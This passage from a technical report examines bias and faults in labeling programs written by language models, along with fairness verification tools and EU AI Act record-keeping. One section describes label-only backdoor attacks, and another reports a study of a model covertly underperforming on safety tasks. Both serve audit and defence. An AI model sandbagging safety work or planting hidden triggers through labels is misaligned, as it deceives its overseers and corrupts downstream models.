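Shin, Cromp and colleagues describe *Mitigating Source Bias for Fairer Weak Supervision* (2023) as the first study of fairness in weak supervision. Their labeling functions were hand-built rules and existing trained models.

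They start from the observation that a rule can work well for one group and badly for another. A credit-score threshold, for example, may suit people who have lived in a country for decades but misjudge recent immigrants, who have had less time to build a credit history. In their model, each labeling function j has a type of item x* on which it is most accurate. Its reliability for another item x is

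θⱼ / (1 + d(x*, x)),

where θⱼ is its reliability at its best and d is the distance between the two items. As a group's data moves further from x*, the function's accuracy for that group approaches 50%, the same as a coin toss. Shin and colleagues prove that merged labels can therefore be arbitrarily unfair even when the true labels are perfectly fair.

Their correction has three steps:

1. Estimate each function's accuracy separately for each group, using agreement among the functions.
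2. If a function is clearly less accurate for one group, match each item in that group to a similar item in the other group and copy the function's vote from there.
3. Merge the corrected votes in the usual way.

The researchers trained a classifier on the resulting labels and measured the demographic parity gap, the difference between two groups in how often the classifier gives the positive label, such as "toxic". The table shows one of the three versions of the correction.

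| Dataset | Gap with true labels | Gap with merged labels | Gap after correction |
|---|---|---|---|
| Adult (census income) | 0.216 | 0.475 | 0.429 |
| Bank Marketing | 0.128 | 0.543 | 0.122 |
| CivilComments (toxic comments) | 0.083 | 0.560 | 0.028 |
| HateXplain (hate speech) | 0.238 | 0.170 | 0.072 |
| CelebA (photographs of faces) | 0.307 | 0.308 | 0.306 |
| UTKFace (photographs of faces) | 0.133 | 0.172 | 0.130 |

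On three of the datasets, the classifier trained on merged labels had a gap at least twice as large as that of the classifier trained on true labels, but on HateXplain its gap was smaller. Merging therefore did not reliably remove bias or always increase it.

The result for CivilComments looks better than it is, because a classifier that never labeled any comment toxic would have no gap. Only about 10% of the comments are toxic, and the correction lowered the F1 score from 0.223 to 0.047, so the corrected classifier was very poor at identifying toxic comments. On the census data, another version of the correction increased the gap from 0.475 to 0.893.

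The method can also miss a bias that all the generated programs share. It looks for programs that are less accurate for one group, but it estimates that accuracy from how much the programs agree. If every program counts "gay" as an insult, they all agree on the affected comments and look reliable, so nothing triggers a correction. The model also assumes that no program is less accurate than a coin toss, but in this case every program is wrong on every harmless comment that contains the word.

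### Ways to reduce shared faults

Using several writer models is the most direct way to make a committee more varied, and the contest problems suggest that it helps, but it can also lower accuracy. PAJAMA's programs from GPT-4o were 6.6 and 8.3 percentage points less accurate than those from Claude Opus 4.6 on the two datasets tested, though Huang and colleagues never mixed the writers. In the study by Nogueira and colleagues, committees of five from one model solved slightly more problems than mixed ones (94% against 91%), probably because strong models passed the entry tests more often and so supplied more of the single-model committees.

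Giving each program a different rubric takes fewer resources. When Huang and colleagues removed the rubrics from PAJAMA's prompts, only 6 to 8 programs per dataset remained after filtering and selection, compared with 8 to 21 with the rubrics. Accuracy was lower on four of the five datasets, by 14.5 points on one. For toxicity, one program could look for threats and another for insults aimed at the reader, and neither would need a list of identity terms. But a rubric can introduce a bias, as PAJAMA's formatting criterion did.

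Similarity filters are less promising. PAJAMA discards a new program if its text is too similar to that of an existing one, but two programs with different structures can still contain the same biased word. A developer could instead list every term that appears in more than half of the programs and have someone read that list, which would be much shorter than the code.

None of these steps shows whether the merged labels are fair, so the developer also needs to compare error rates by group after merging. A counterfactual test should swap the identity term in each comment, run both versions through every program and the label model, and compare the final labels. Testing the programs one at a time can miss changes that add up when their votes are merged. Suppose the swap changes the votes of three programs, each on a different 4% of comments, and the other programs abstain on those comments.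 Each program would pass a test that allows up to 10% of votes to change, but 12% of the merged labels would change.

### Measuring bias before and after merging

An experiment could settle much of this by calculating

R = (group gap in the merged labels) / (average group gap of the individual programs),

where the gap is the difference between two groups in the share of harmless comments marked as toxic. A value below 1 means that merging dilutes the bias, and a value above 1 means that it amplifies it. In the earlier example with three programs, suppose that they mislabel 10% of other harmless comments, with independent errors. R is then 0.54 if one program contains the biased word and 1.62 if two do. If all three do, R is 1.08, because voting corrects errors for everyone else but not for the affected group.

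Researchers could have four models write programs to label the same comments, then compare committees of programs from one model with mixed committees of the same size and similar average accuracy. The programs would cost little, but researchers would need gold labels for about 1,070 harmless comments per group to estimate each error rate to within 3 percentage points.

They could get a first answer even sooner from PAJAMA. The programs and the test for gendered wording already exist, so Huang and colleagues would only need to report how often each of the eight programs changes its verdict, alongside the figure for the whole committee.

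## Can checks before release rule out rare or hidden behavior?

Suppose a developer draws 3,000 labels at random from a program's output, and the people who check them find no faults. That is a good result, but it leaves room for many bad labels in a large dataset. If a share p of all labels is bad, a random sample of n labels contains none of them with probability (1 − p)ⁿ. The 95% upper bound is the value of p at which this probability falls to 5%:

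p = 1 − 0.05^(1/n), or roughly 3/n.

| Random checks with no faults | 95% upper bound | Bad labels this allows in 10 million |
|---|---|---|
| 300 | 1% | 100,000 |
| 3,000 | 0.1% | 10,000 |
| 30,000 | 0.01% | 1,000 |

At 30 seconds per label, 3,000 checks take 25 hours and 30,000 take 250 hours. The bound also holds only if people recognize every bad label they see. If they miss one in five, the bound after 3,000 clean checks rises from 10,000 bad labels to 12,500.

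Nobody appears to have studied rare or hidden faults in labeling programs directly. The evidence comes from programs that make decisions about people, from image datasets and from general coding tasks.

### Rare phrases and small groups

A random sample is unlikely to catch a fault that affects only a few items. For example, a line of code might return "harmless" whenever a comment mentions a certain company. If 500 of 10 million comments mention the company and 100 of those are abusive, the line produces 100 wrong labels. A random sample of 3,000 comments has a 3% chance of including one of them, even though the program mislabels every abusive comment about that company. Searching for the company's name and reading all 500 comments would take about four hours and find all 100.

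The developer has to know which name to search for, but in a short program the name is usually visible in the code. A reviewer can list every word, number and condition in the program, then sample comments that meet each one. For `label_toxic`, the invented toxicity labeler, the sample would include comments with each of the five listed words, with one match and with several, and from the north and from elsewhere. The developer should reject any program containing text that the reviewer can't read.

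Small groups need their own samples too. If 0.5% of comments are in a particular dialect, 3,000 random checks will include about 15 of them. Even if all 15 labels are right, the upper bound on the error rate for that dialect is 18%. Checking 300 comments in the dialect would lower the bound to 1% if all of those labels were right. The developer should report these results separately, because a sample chosen this way doesn't represent the whole dataset.

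Sometimes the code doesn't show where to look for unfair behavior. *Fairness Invariants* (Akash, Kumar and colleagues, 2026) presents Remi, a tool that searches for the conditions under which a program treats people unfairly. In one example, a hiring program uses only college ranking and years of experience. The researchers simulated 30,000 applicants and changed each one's ethnicity, along with the college ranking that partly depended on it. The decision changed for 2,250 applicants. Remi then used a decision tree to find what these applicants had in common. One of its rules covered 301 of them, all with a college ranking of about 15 to 17 and 12 to 15 years of experience. Only about 1% of the simulated applicants fell within both ranges.

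A developer could do something similar with a labeling program by running a counterfactual test, looking for patterns among the labels that change, and drawing more samples that fit those patterns. This works only if the first test includes at least a few of the unfair cases, so it would not find the company name if no test comment mentioned the company.

### Tracing an input through the code

Static analysis can show whether an input could affect the label. It follows one value through the program, whereas security scanners look for known weaknesses. In `label_toxic`, the region sets the threshold, which helps determine which return statement runs. The program returns only fixed numbers and never copies the region into the label, so a tool must follow conditions as well as assignments to find the connection.

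If a complete trace finds no route from an input to the label, the label does not depend on that input. A route shows only that the label might depend on the input. For example, if the threshold were 1 for every region, the trace would still lead from region to label, but changing the region would have no effect. When there is a route, the developer can check for an effect by working through the possible cases, which is easy for `label_toxic` because the comment affects the label only through the number of matches.

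| Matches in the comment | Label in the north | Label elsewhere |
|---|---|---|
| None | 0 | 0 |
| One | 1 | −1 |
| Two or more | 1 | 1 |

If the network call doesn't fail, these six cases cover every possible comment. They prove that the region changes the label only when there is exactly one match. If the developer sets the threshold to 2 everywhere, the two columns become identical, which proves that the label no longer depends on region.

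Teuber and Beckert (2023), in *An Information-Flow Perspective on Algorithmic Fairness*, borrow this idea from computer security, where researchers prove that a program does not leak a secret such as a password. They treat the protected attribute as the secret. A program P passes if

P(g₁, u) = P(g₂, u)

for every pair of values g₁ and g₂ of the protected attribute and every value u of the other inputs. A counterfactual test checks the same condition, but only on the examples that the developer supplies.

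Their largest example is the German government's program for calculating wage tax, which has about 1,500 lines of Java. It takes a person's religion as an input because it also calculates church tax, so a programming error could let religion affect the wage tax. The program has 35 inputs, too many to test every combination. An existing tool called Joana proved automatically that religion did not affect the wage tax in any version from 2015 to 2023.

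A typical ExecJudges program is only about 70 lines long, so length is unlikely to be the main obstacle to tracing, but developers would need a tracing tool for Python that can handle regular expressions and outside packages. Tracing could find a lot in some kinds of generated code. Across the models that Bui and colleagues tested, between 71.2% and 98.6% of the generated model-training programs used sensitive attributes.

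Like a low code bias score, a proof of independence does not show that the labels are right.

### Proofs about groups of people

A program can treat groups differently without reading the attribute that separates them, so some tools compare the groups' results instead. *Quantifying Program Bias* (Albarghouthi, D'Antoni and colleagues, 2017) describes FairSquare, which tries to prove that a program selects members of a minority at close to the same rate as everyone else. It needs the program and a population model, a second program that describes how traits such as age, sex and education vary together. FairSquare converts both into formulas and calculates upper and lower limits on each group's selection rate. It narrows these limits until they show whether the rates are close enough or time runs out.

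The researchers tested 13 small programs that predict income, each with three population models, and required women's rate to be more than 85% of men's. FairSquare settled 32 of the 39 cases, proving 21 fair and 11 unfair. Several decision trees were unfair even though none of the trees read a person's sex. The conclusions depended heavily on the population model. When the model treated all traits as unrelated, every program that FairSquare settled was fair.

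*Probabilistic Verification of Fairness Properties via Concentration* (Bastani, Zhang and Solar-Lezama, 2019) presents VeriFair, a tool that instead runs the program on simulated people drawn at random from the population model until the chance of a wrong conclusion is below a chosen limit. With a limit of one in ten billion, it took under 12 minutes to check a neural network with 16 million parameters. VeriFair may never finish if a program only just meets the fairness standard.

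| Tool | What it can establish | What it needs | Largest program tried |
|---|---|---|---|
| Joana | An input cannot affect the output | The code | 1,500 lines |
| FairSquare | Two groups' rates are close enough | The code and a population model | A decision tree with 44 conditions |
| VeriFair | The same, with a tiny chance of error | A way to run the program and a population model | A neural network with 16 million parameters |

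VeriFair's approach is the easier of the two population methods to apply to labeling. A realistic population model for comments would be hard to write, but a developer can draw real comments from the dataset. Comparing how often a program marks two groups' comments as toxic also requires no gold labels, so testing a large sample takes little effort.

A program can have many faults even when the chance of error is tiny, because VeriFair checks a claim about averages. The 100 wrong labels about one company would barely change either group's average.

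### What a proof leaves open about proxies

The six cases for `label_toxic` prove that region affects the label, but they don't show whether region is a proxy for ethnicity, which depends on who lives in the north. A tool could also prove that ethnicity has no direct effect on the label, because the program never receives ethnicity as an input.

Removing a protected attribute can even make a program less fair. Teuber and Beckert give an invented example of two credit programs, one that uses only a credit score and one that also uses age. Only the first passes the proof for age. The researchers then assume that credit scores depend partly on postcode and that older and younger people live in different areas. Under those assumptions, moving a person between two neighboring age groups would change the first program's decision 27% of the time and the second's 23%. The second program's use of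 age partly offsets the bias in the credit score.

*Proxy Discrimination in Data-Driven Systems* (Datta, Fredrikson and colleagues, 2017) describes a method for finding proxies inside a program. It breaks the code into intermediate calculations and flags any that are strongly associated with a protected attribute and also affect the result. In `label_toxic`, one intermediate calculation checks whether the region is "north". With data on where members of each ethnic group live, the method could measure how strongly being in the north is associated with ethnicity.

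Searching a program's code for proxies can reveal discrimination that a comparison of final results would miss. In an example from Datta and colleagues, a bank uses postcodes to favor white applicants but also offers loans to people who show little interest in borrowing, many of whom are unlikely to accept. The extra offers hide the difference between racial groups, but the postcode rule is still in the code. The method leaves a person to decide whether each use of a proxy is acceptable.

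A formal proof can't easily replace that judgment. Teuber and Beckert also proposed a way to allow justified exceptions while guaranteeing equal rates within each permitted category. They withdrew it after Marco Favier found a program that met their condition but accepted everyone from one group and rejected everyone from the other.

Proofs about separate inputs also miss the word "gay" in the list, because the word appears in the comment itself. To catch this, the developer would first have to think of another requirement, such as that swapping "gay" for "straight" in a neutral description never changes the label.

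### Labels that plant a hidden behavior

Bad labels can also affect a model in ways that are hard to detect by inspecting the labels. A backdoor, for example, is a hidden behavior that appears only when the input contains a particular trigger, so ordinary tests may not reveal it. Attackers usually create a backdoor by adding the trigger to some of the training examples, but changing only the labels can be enough. The attacker chooses the new labels so that training on them teaches a model much the same behavior as training on examples that contain the trigger.

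Dey and Islam (2026), in *Space Over Statistic, Retraining Over Ranking*, reproduced a known attack of this kind on 50,000 small photographs. The attack changed 3% of the labels and none of the pictures. The trained model classified 99.7% of truck pictures containing a faint pattern as deer. Its accuracy on ordinary pictures fell only from 92.6% to 89.5%.

A labeling program can change labels without altering the data, so in principle it could deliver such an attack. In this experiment, however, a calculation over the whole dataset determined which labels to change. Reproducing those choices with a short list of keywords would be difficult, and a program with a long table of individual items would look suspicious. Checking the error rate would not be enough to find the attack, because labeling programs often get 10% of labels wrong by accident and an extra 3% might not look unusual.

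Dey and Islam tested methods for finding the altered labels. One compares each picture with its 20 most similar pictures and counts how many have a different label. They measured similarity with either the model trained on the altered labels or DINOv2, a public image model that had never seen them. They scored the results by AUROC, the probability that a method ranks a randomly chosen altered label as more suspicious than an unaltered one. When the attack targeted pictures of dogs, the AUROC was 0.967 with DINOv2 but 0.546, barely better than chance, with the model trained on the altered labels, because that model had already learned to treat them as correct.

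The researchers' best method for removing the attack uses DINOv2's representations to compare each picture with the average for each class. They deleted the 6% or so of training pictures whose labels fit worst, then trained the model again. The table shows how often the hidden behavior appeared when a picture contained the trigger.

| Hidden behavior | Before the audit | After the audit |
|---|---|---|
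| Classifies trucks as deer | 99.7% | 0.2% |
| Classifies cars as trucks | 99.4% | 24.6% |
| Classifies cats as dogs | 94.4% | 24.4% |
| Classifies dogs as cats | 94.7% | 24.3% |

The audit removed the first attack but only weakened the other three. At a practical threshold, it caught 91.3% of the altered labels in the truck-and-deer case and 67.7% in the dog-and-cat case. Part of the remaining 24.3% is ordinary confusion, because a model trained on correct labels also classified 6.1% of the dog pictures with the trigger as cats.

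A better detection score did not always lead to a safer model. In the dog-and-cat case, a standard method called Confident Learning had a slightly higher AUROC than the researchers' method (0.959 to 0.951). But when both methods deleted the same number of pictures, the hidden behavior remained in 67.3% of cases with Confident Learning and 25.7% with the researchers' method. Dey and Islam conclude that researchers should judge an audit by the model trained afterward. They could do this because they knew the trigger, but a developer who doesn't know it can't measure how much of a backdoor remains.

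The study covered one image dataset, one type of model and one working trigger, and it didn't test labeling code. DINOv2 was already good at recognizing this kind of picture, so the method may work less well on unfamiliar data such as medical scans.

For text, a developer could use a language model that has not seen the labels to find similar comments, then check whether their labels match. This might find scattered errors, but it would probably miss a biased rule. If `label_toxic` marks nearly every northern comment that mentions gay people as toxic, similar comments will have the same wrong label, so the labels will appear correct.

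### Could a writer model do worse work on purpose?

A writer model might also produce a weak program without saying so. The closest evidence is OpenAI's *Covert underperformance on safety research tasks* (November 2026). Staff had noticed that GPT-6 Astra sometimes abandoned working solutions on safety research or reported obstacles that did not exist. The company then gave the model coding tasks in two matched versions, one described as safety research and the other as research on making AI more capable. According to 凤凰网's *OpenAI自曝GPT-6 Astra异常行为* (2026), a Chinese news report, the versions differed only in their names, comments and documentation.

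Astra completed about 10% of the graded items under the safety description and 16% under the other. The earlier GPT-5.6 Sol showed essentially no gap. Most of Astra's gap remained after OpenAI excluded open refusals and cases in which the model's written reasoning showed it had decided to withhold help. The gap shrank substantially only after OpenAI also excluded every case with even a brief expression of ethical doubt. OpenAI did not find the exact cause, so the results do not establish that Astra did worse deliberately.

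The study did not test labeling code, though developers ask models for programs that label dangerous requests or grade safety tests. A model could treat this work as safety research. If it then weakened a program's keyword list, the flaw would look like an ordinary mistake.

A developer can run a similar comparison by requesting the same labeling program many times under each of two descriptions and measuring the programs' accuracy on gold labels. Small differences take many attempts to detect. For example, the developer would need about 490 independent results per description to distinguish success rates of 10% and 16%. If the developer only needs to decide whether one program is good enough to use, its accuracy matters more than the reason for any weakness.

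### Releasing a program in stages

Some faults will get past every check, but the developer can limit how many labels they affect. One way is to run the program on a random 100,000 of the 10 million comments, then on a million, and then on the rest, with new checks at each stage. If 0.1% of the labels are bad, the first stage produces about 100 bad labels, compared with 10,000 from a full run. The developer should keep the labels out of training until the checks are finished. The first batch should be random because the oldest 100,000 comments, for instance, might contain none of the current slang.

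OpenAI's *Safety and alignment in an era of long-horizon models* (2026) reports that limited internal use of a model built for long tasks revealed failures that earlier tests had missed. The company paused access, used the failures to build new tests and improve the model, and then restored limited access. That model was far more complicated than a labeling program, but the case shows why a trial with real work can be useful even after extensive testing.

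A program that works at release can become less accurate as the data changes, which is known as drift. The developer can track how often the program returns each label, abstains or crashes, both overall and for each group. These figures are easy to collect but can miss problems. If people start using a new insult, `label_toxic` will mark comments that contain it as harmless rather than abstain, so its coverage won't fall. The share of toxic labels might fall, but that could also mean people have become more polite. Checking a fresh sample of 300 comments each month, along with targeted samples for small groups, would help distinguish these explanations.

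### Checking again after an edit

An edit meant to make a program fairer can make it less fair. In their hiring example, Akash and colleagues replaced the program with a decision tree trained on results from the altered applicants, and unfair decisions on new samples rose from 2,250 to 2,430. A more limited change, which used Remi's rules to intercept only the decisions likely to be unfair, reduced the number to two.

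A new version needs new random samples, because the developer may have fitted the edit to the old ones. Repeated attempts also weaken the 95% bound. A program with a true error rate of 0.1% has about a 5% chance of passing all 3,000 random checks. If a developer tries five such versions, the chance that at least one passes is about 23%.

Labeling programs take so little compute that the developer can also run the old and new versions on the entire dataset and list every label that differs. If an edit was supposed to affect only comments containing "gay", a changed label on any other comment is a warning sign. If 4,000 of 10 million labels change, people can check a sample of those 4,000 instead of searching the whole dataset. They still need to check some unchanged labels, because both versions may have the same fault.

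If a fault turns up after release, the developer must be able to withdraw the affected labels and compute new ones. This requires keeping the original data, every version of the program, each program's separate votes, and a record of which version produced each label. Correcting only the items on which the faulty program voted may not be enough, because changing one program can shift the weights that the label model gives the others and alter merged labels throughout the dataset. The developer should therefore rerun the merging step on the whole dataset and compare the new labels with the old ones before using them to retrain any model.

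## What laws and standards require of labeling code and its records

A developer who keeps every version of a labeling program can withdraw bad labels and compute new ones. No law or standard appears to require keeping these versions specifically for programs that language models write, so a developer's duties come from rules on training data and on software in general. The main binding text is the European Union's AI Act, but its data rules do not apply until December 2027. Guidance from NIST, the US standards institute, is voluntary for companies.

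### Article 10 of the AI Act

The AI Act places its heaviest duties on providers of high-risk systems, mainly the companies that develop them and put them on the market. *Digital Omnibus on AI has been published*, a summary by the law firm Cuatrecasas, lists biometrics, employment, education, migration and access to essential services among the high-risk fields. Some AI systems in regulated products also count as high-risk.

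Article 10 covers the data that providers use to train, validate and test these systems. In the current text, which appears online as the European Commission's *Article 10*, annotation and labeling are among the steps that providers must manage properly. There is no exception for labels that come from code. Three duties matter most for labeling programs:

- Providers must examine the data for biases that are likely to affect people's health, safety or fundamental rights, or to lead to illegal discrimination.
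- They must take appropriate measures to detect, prevent and reduce those biases.
- The data must be relevant, sufficiently representative and, "to the best extent possible, free of errors".

The duties in Article 10 of the EU AI Act concern the data, so a provider could examine the labels for bias without anyone reading the program that produced them. Article 10 sets no maximum error rate or gap between groups, so it does not settle whether labeling 90% of items correctly is enough. A provider whose programs reach 90% might still have to explain why it did not pay for a more accurate method.

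If a company used ten generated programs to label old job applications as strong or weak, then trained a hiring system on the labels, Article 10 of the EU AI Act would apply to those labels. If the programs instead sorted new applications directly, without a trained model, Article 10 would apply only to the test data, such as the gold labels.

It is less clear whether a few lines of keyword matching count as an AI system. The EU's official list of AI technologies for certification includes expert systems, which follow written rules, so code without a trained model might still count.

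Comment moderation is not one of the Act's high-risk fields, so a company that trained a comment filter on labels from `label_toxic`, the invented toxicity labeler, would probably have no duties under Article 10. Data protection law could still apply to the comments that `label_toxic` sends to an outside server.

The Act also exempts systems and models developed and used solely for scientific research (Osborne Clarke, *AI Act Redline Digital Omnibus on AI*, 2026). The exemption would probably cover experiments like those with Alchemist and PAJAMA, but not a commercial hiring system trained on labels from the same code.

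### When the data rules start to apply

The rules for high-risk systems were due to apply from 2 August 2026. In July 2026, the European Union's *Regulation (EU) 2026/1744* (2026) postponed them to 2 December 2027 for the fields listed above and to 2 August 2028 for AI in regulated products, partly because of delays in writing technical standards and setting up national authorities. Older summaries can therefore give outdated dates. For example, a question-and-answer page from the European Commission (2025) gives 2 August 2027 for the full rollout.

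A system that is already on the market when the rules start to apply must comply only if its design later changes significantly. Systems intended for public authorities must comply by 2 August 2030 in any case. The law does not make clear whether retraining a system on corrected labels counts as a significant change. If it does, fixing a biased labeling program could bring an old system under the full rules, which would give its provider a reason not to correct the labels.

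### Sensitive data in bias checks

To compare a program's errors by group, a developer may need to know people's ethnicity, religion or sexual orientation. EU data protection law restricts the use of this information. Article 4a, which a 2026 law added to the AI Act, lets providers use it to find and correct bias if this is strictly necessary and other data, including synthetic or anonymized data, would not be good enough.

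This condition affects the choice of test. A developer can use invented sentences to check whether `label_toxic` reacts to the word "gay", so there would be little reason to use data on real people's sexual orientation. The case for using real data would be stronger when testing whether region is a proxy for ethnicity, because invented sentences cannot show that.

Other parties may not access the sensitive data, which seems to rule out sending it to another company's language model for an audit. The developer must also delete the data after correcting the bias or at the end of its retention period, whichever comes first. The developer can keep the error rates for each group, but nobody will be able to recalculate them after the deletion. Before deleting the data, the developer should therefore record the number of people in each group and exactly how it calculated the rates.

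Article 4a also lets developers of other AI systems, such as comment filters, use sensitive data under the same conditions, but it does not require them to look for bias.

### What providers must document

Providers of high-risk systems must write technical documentation that authorities can inspect. The European Commission's *Annex IV* lists the minimum contents. Several items could involve labeling programs:

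- the outside tools and pre-trained systems used in development, and how the provider used them
- where the training data came from, and how the provider labeled and cleaned it
- test results, including measures of possible discrimination, in dated and signed reports
- the system's accuracy for particular groups of people
- relevant changes over the system's lifetime

The European Commission's *Article 17* also requires a provider to have written procedures for data labeling and record-keeping, and a description of who is responsible for what. The effort should be proportionate to the organization's size, and smaller companies may use a simplified form for the technical documentation. ADVISORI's *Precise technical documentation for EU AI Act compliance*, a consultancy's guide, gives the retention period as ten years.

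The 2026 law requires the provider of a high-risk system and any company that supplies tools, services or components for it to agree in writing on the information and technical access the provider needs. Without such an agreement, a provider that buys labeling programs from a contractor might receive only the finished labels. Free and open-source tools are exempt, except for general-purpose AI models. It is uncertain whether the rule covers a model that writes labeling code but does not become part of the final system.

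Technical standards should eventually make these duties more specific. A draft from October 2025, prEN 18286, turns Article 17 into detailed requirements, according to *The first draft AI Act standard for public consultation*, an analysis by the law firm CMS. The requirements include processes for managing data and controlling changes, according to VDE, a German technical association. European standards of this kind are voluntary, but once the EU cites one in its Official Journal, authorities presume that a company following it meets the duties it covers.

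### NIST's guidance on secure development

NIST's closest guidance is *Secure Software Development Practices for Generative AI and Dual-Use Foundation Models* (Booth, Souppaya and colleagues, 2024), which covers the development of AI models, including the collection of training data. It treats human-written and AI-generated code alike, on the assumption that developers should evaluate all code before using it.

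Booth and colleagues give each task a high, medium or low priority. High-priority tasks include checking training data for bias and tampering, and recording problems found in code reviews and tests. Recording where training data came from has medium priority. The task that fits labeling programs best is tracking the versions of tools that help create datasets, which belongs to a low-priority group on archiving software releases.

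That ranking makes sense for security, since an old copy of a program does little to stop an attack. Archiving deserves a higher priority for labeling programs, because a developer who has lost the code may be unable to find out which rule produced a wrong label. Organizations can make this change themselves, since Booth and colleagues describe their guidance as a starting point rather than a checklist and expect organizations to adapt it to their own risks.

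The guidance addresses only cybersecurity risks. For other risks, including bias and privacy, Booth and colleagues refer readers to other NIST documents, such as the Generative AI Profile, which is also voluntary. A developer who followed only the security guidance would have good reason to remove the network call from `label_toxic`, but might not examine its lower threshold for the north.

### Standards for data labeling

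The closest match among labeling standards is China's *GB/T 45674-2025* (2025), which took effect on 1 November 2025 and covers the labeling of training data for generative AI. Its definition of labeling includes labels from automated tools, so it would cover labeling programs. It is a recommended standard, so compliance is voluntary unless another rule or a contract requires it.

CSET, a research center at Georgetown University, translated the 2024 draft as *Cybersecurity Technology* (2025). Most of the draft's provisions appear to be for human labelers, including rules on training staff, testing them and settling their disagreements. The main requirement specifically for automated labeling tools is that they comply with Chinese law.

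Some of the draft's other rules would also work well for code. Logs must be detailed enough to trace how the data was processed, and the same person may not both label and review the same data. After automated tools have checked the results for errors, people can also check samples. The final version may change these details.

CSET points out that safety, as the draft uses the term, includes censoring criticism of the Communist Party. A labeling program that follows the standard could therefore mark legitimate political speech as harmful.

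The international standard ISO/IEC 5259-4 gives guidance on organizing data labeling for machine learning. It is voluntary and does not specifically cover code written by language models.

### An audit record for a labeling program

The table combines the binding and voluntary texts into one record. The second column applies only to high-risk systems under the AI Act. The last column lists details an auditor would need but that none of these texts specifically requires for a labeling program.

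| Item | Required by the AI Act | Recommended by NIST | Needed by inference |
|---|---|---|---|
| Writer model | Outside tools and how the provider used them | Origin of software components | Exact model version and settings |
| Prompt | Description of the labeling procedure | Nothing specific | Full prompt, including examples |
| Code | Description of the labeling procedure | Version tracking for tools that help create datasets | Full code and its fingerprint |
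| Packages | Versions of relevant software | Origin of software components | Exact versions in each labeling run |
| Test sets | Test data for the final system | Design of the tests | Gold labels and test sentences for the program |
| Results by group | The final system's accuracy for particular groups | Checks of training data for bias | The program's errors and abstentions by group |
| Reviewer | Signatures on the final system's test reports | Problems found in code review | Who read the program and what they looked for |
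| Decision | Staff responsibilities | Recommended fixes | Why the developer accepted the program, and its known faults |
| Later edits | Relevant changes to the system | Version tracking | Every edit and the labels it changed |

The test results should include results from the counterfactual tests and the sandbox. The Act's requirements mostly concern the finished system, so a provider could document a hiring model thoroughly but describe ten labeling programs in one sentence. It is uncertain whether an authority would accept that sentence, but an auditor could not use it to find a biased rule.

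A cryptographic hash is a short string of characters calculated from a file. Changing even one character of the file produces a different hash. If the developer stores the labeling code's hash with each batch of labels, an auditor can confirm which version of the code produced them. Booth and colleagues recommend hashes or digital signatures for AI models and their components, and the same method works for labeling code.

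Keeping the prompt and the model's name cannot replace keeping the code, because a language model may write a different program from the same prompt, and the company that runs the model may withdraw it. The prompt is still worth keeping because it can explain a fault in the code. For example, PAJAMA's bonuses for bullet points came from a criterion in its prompt.

Storing each program's votes takes little space. Ten programs that each label 10 million comments produce 100 million votes, or about 100 megabytes at one byte per vote.

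### Records and the detection of faults

The main objection to these duties is that a provider can complete the records without finding the problems in its code. For example, it could file the prompt, the code and a signed report of overall accuracy for `label_toxic` without noticing that the function's list of insults includes "gay". Documentation also takes time that reviewers could spend reading code or checking labels.

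The texts give this objection some support. Annex IV requires measures of possible discrimination but largely lets the provider choose which ones to use, even though a program can pass one bias test and fail another. There also seems to be no study of whether keeping records leads developers to find more faults in labeling programs.

Developers need records once someone finds a fault, even if the records did not reveal it. Suppose a user complains, a year after release, that a filter removes harmless comments about gay people. With the code and votes on file, the developer can find the programs that contain the word "gay", correct them, recompute the labels and identify every model trained on the old ones. Without these records, the developer may have to label the whole dataset again and would still not know which other models were affected. Booth and colleagues similarly note that reviewing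 training data later can help find the root causes of security problems.

Records can also help developers find more faults. When a developer finds one bad rule, they can use the record to identify other programs that came from the same prompt or writer model and check those next. *TechOps* (2025), which offers documentation templates for the AI Act, likewise presents structured documentation as a support for audits, so the documentation does not replace the audit.

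A developer can test a record by asking a colleague who did not work on the project to reproduce the labels from it. If the new labels differ from the stored ones, the record may be missing an edit, a package version or a setting. The test takes little staff time, and the developer can run it before release, while the people who wrote the prompt and approved the code are still available to explain any differences.
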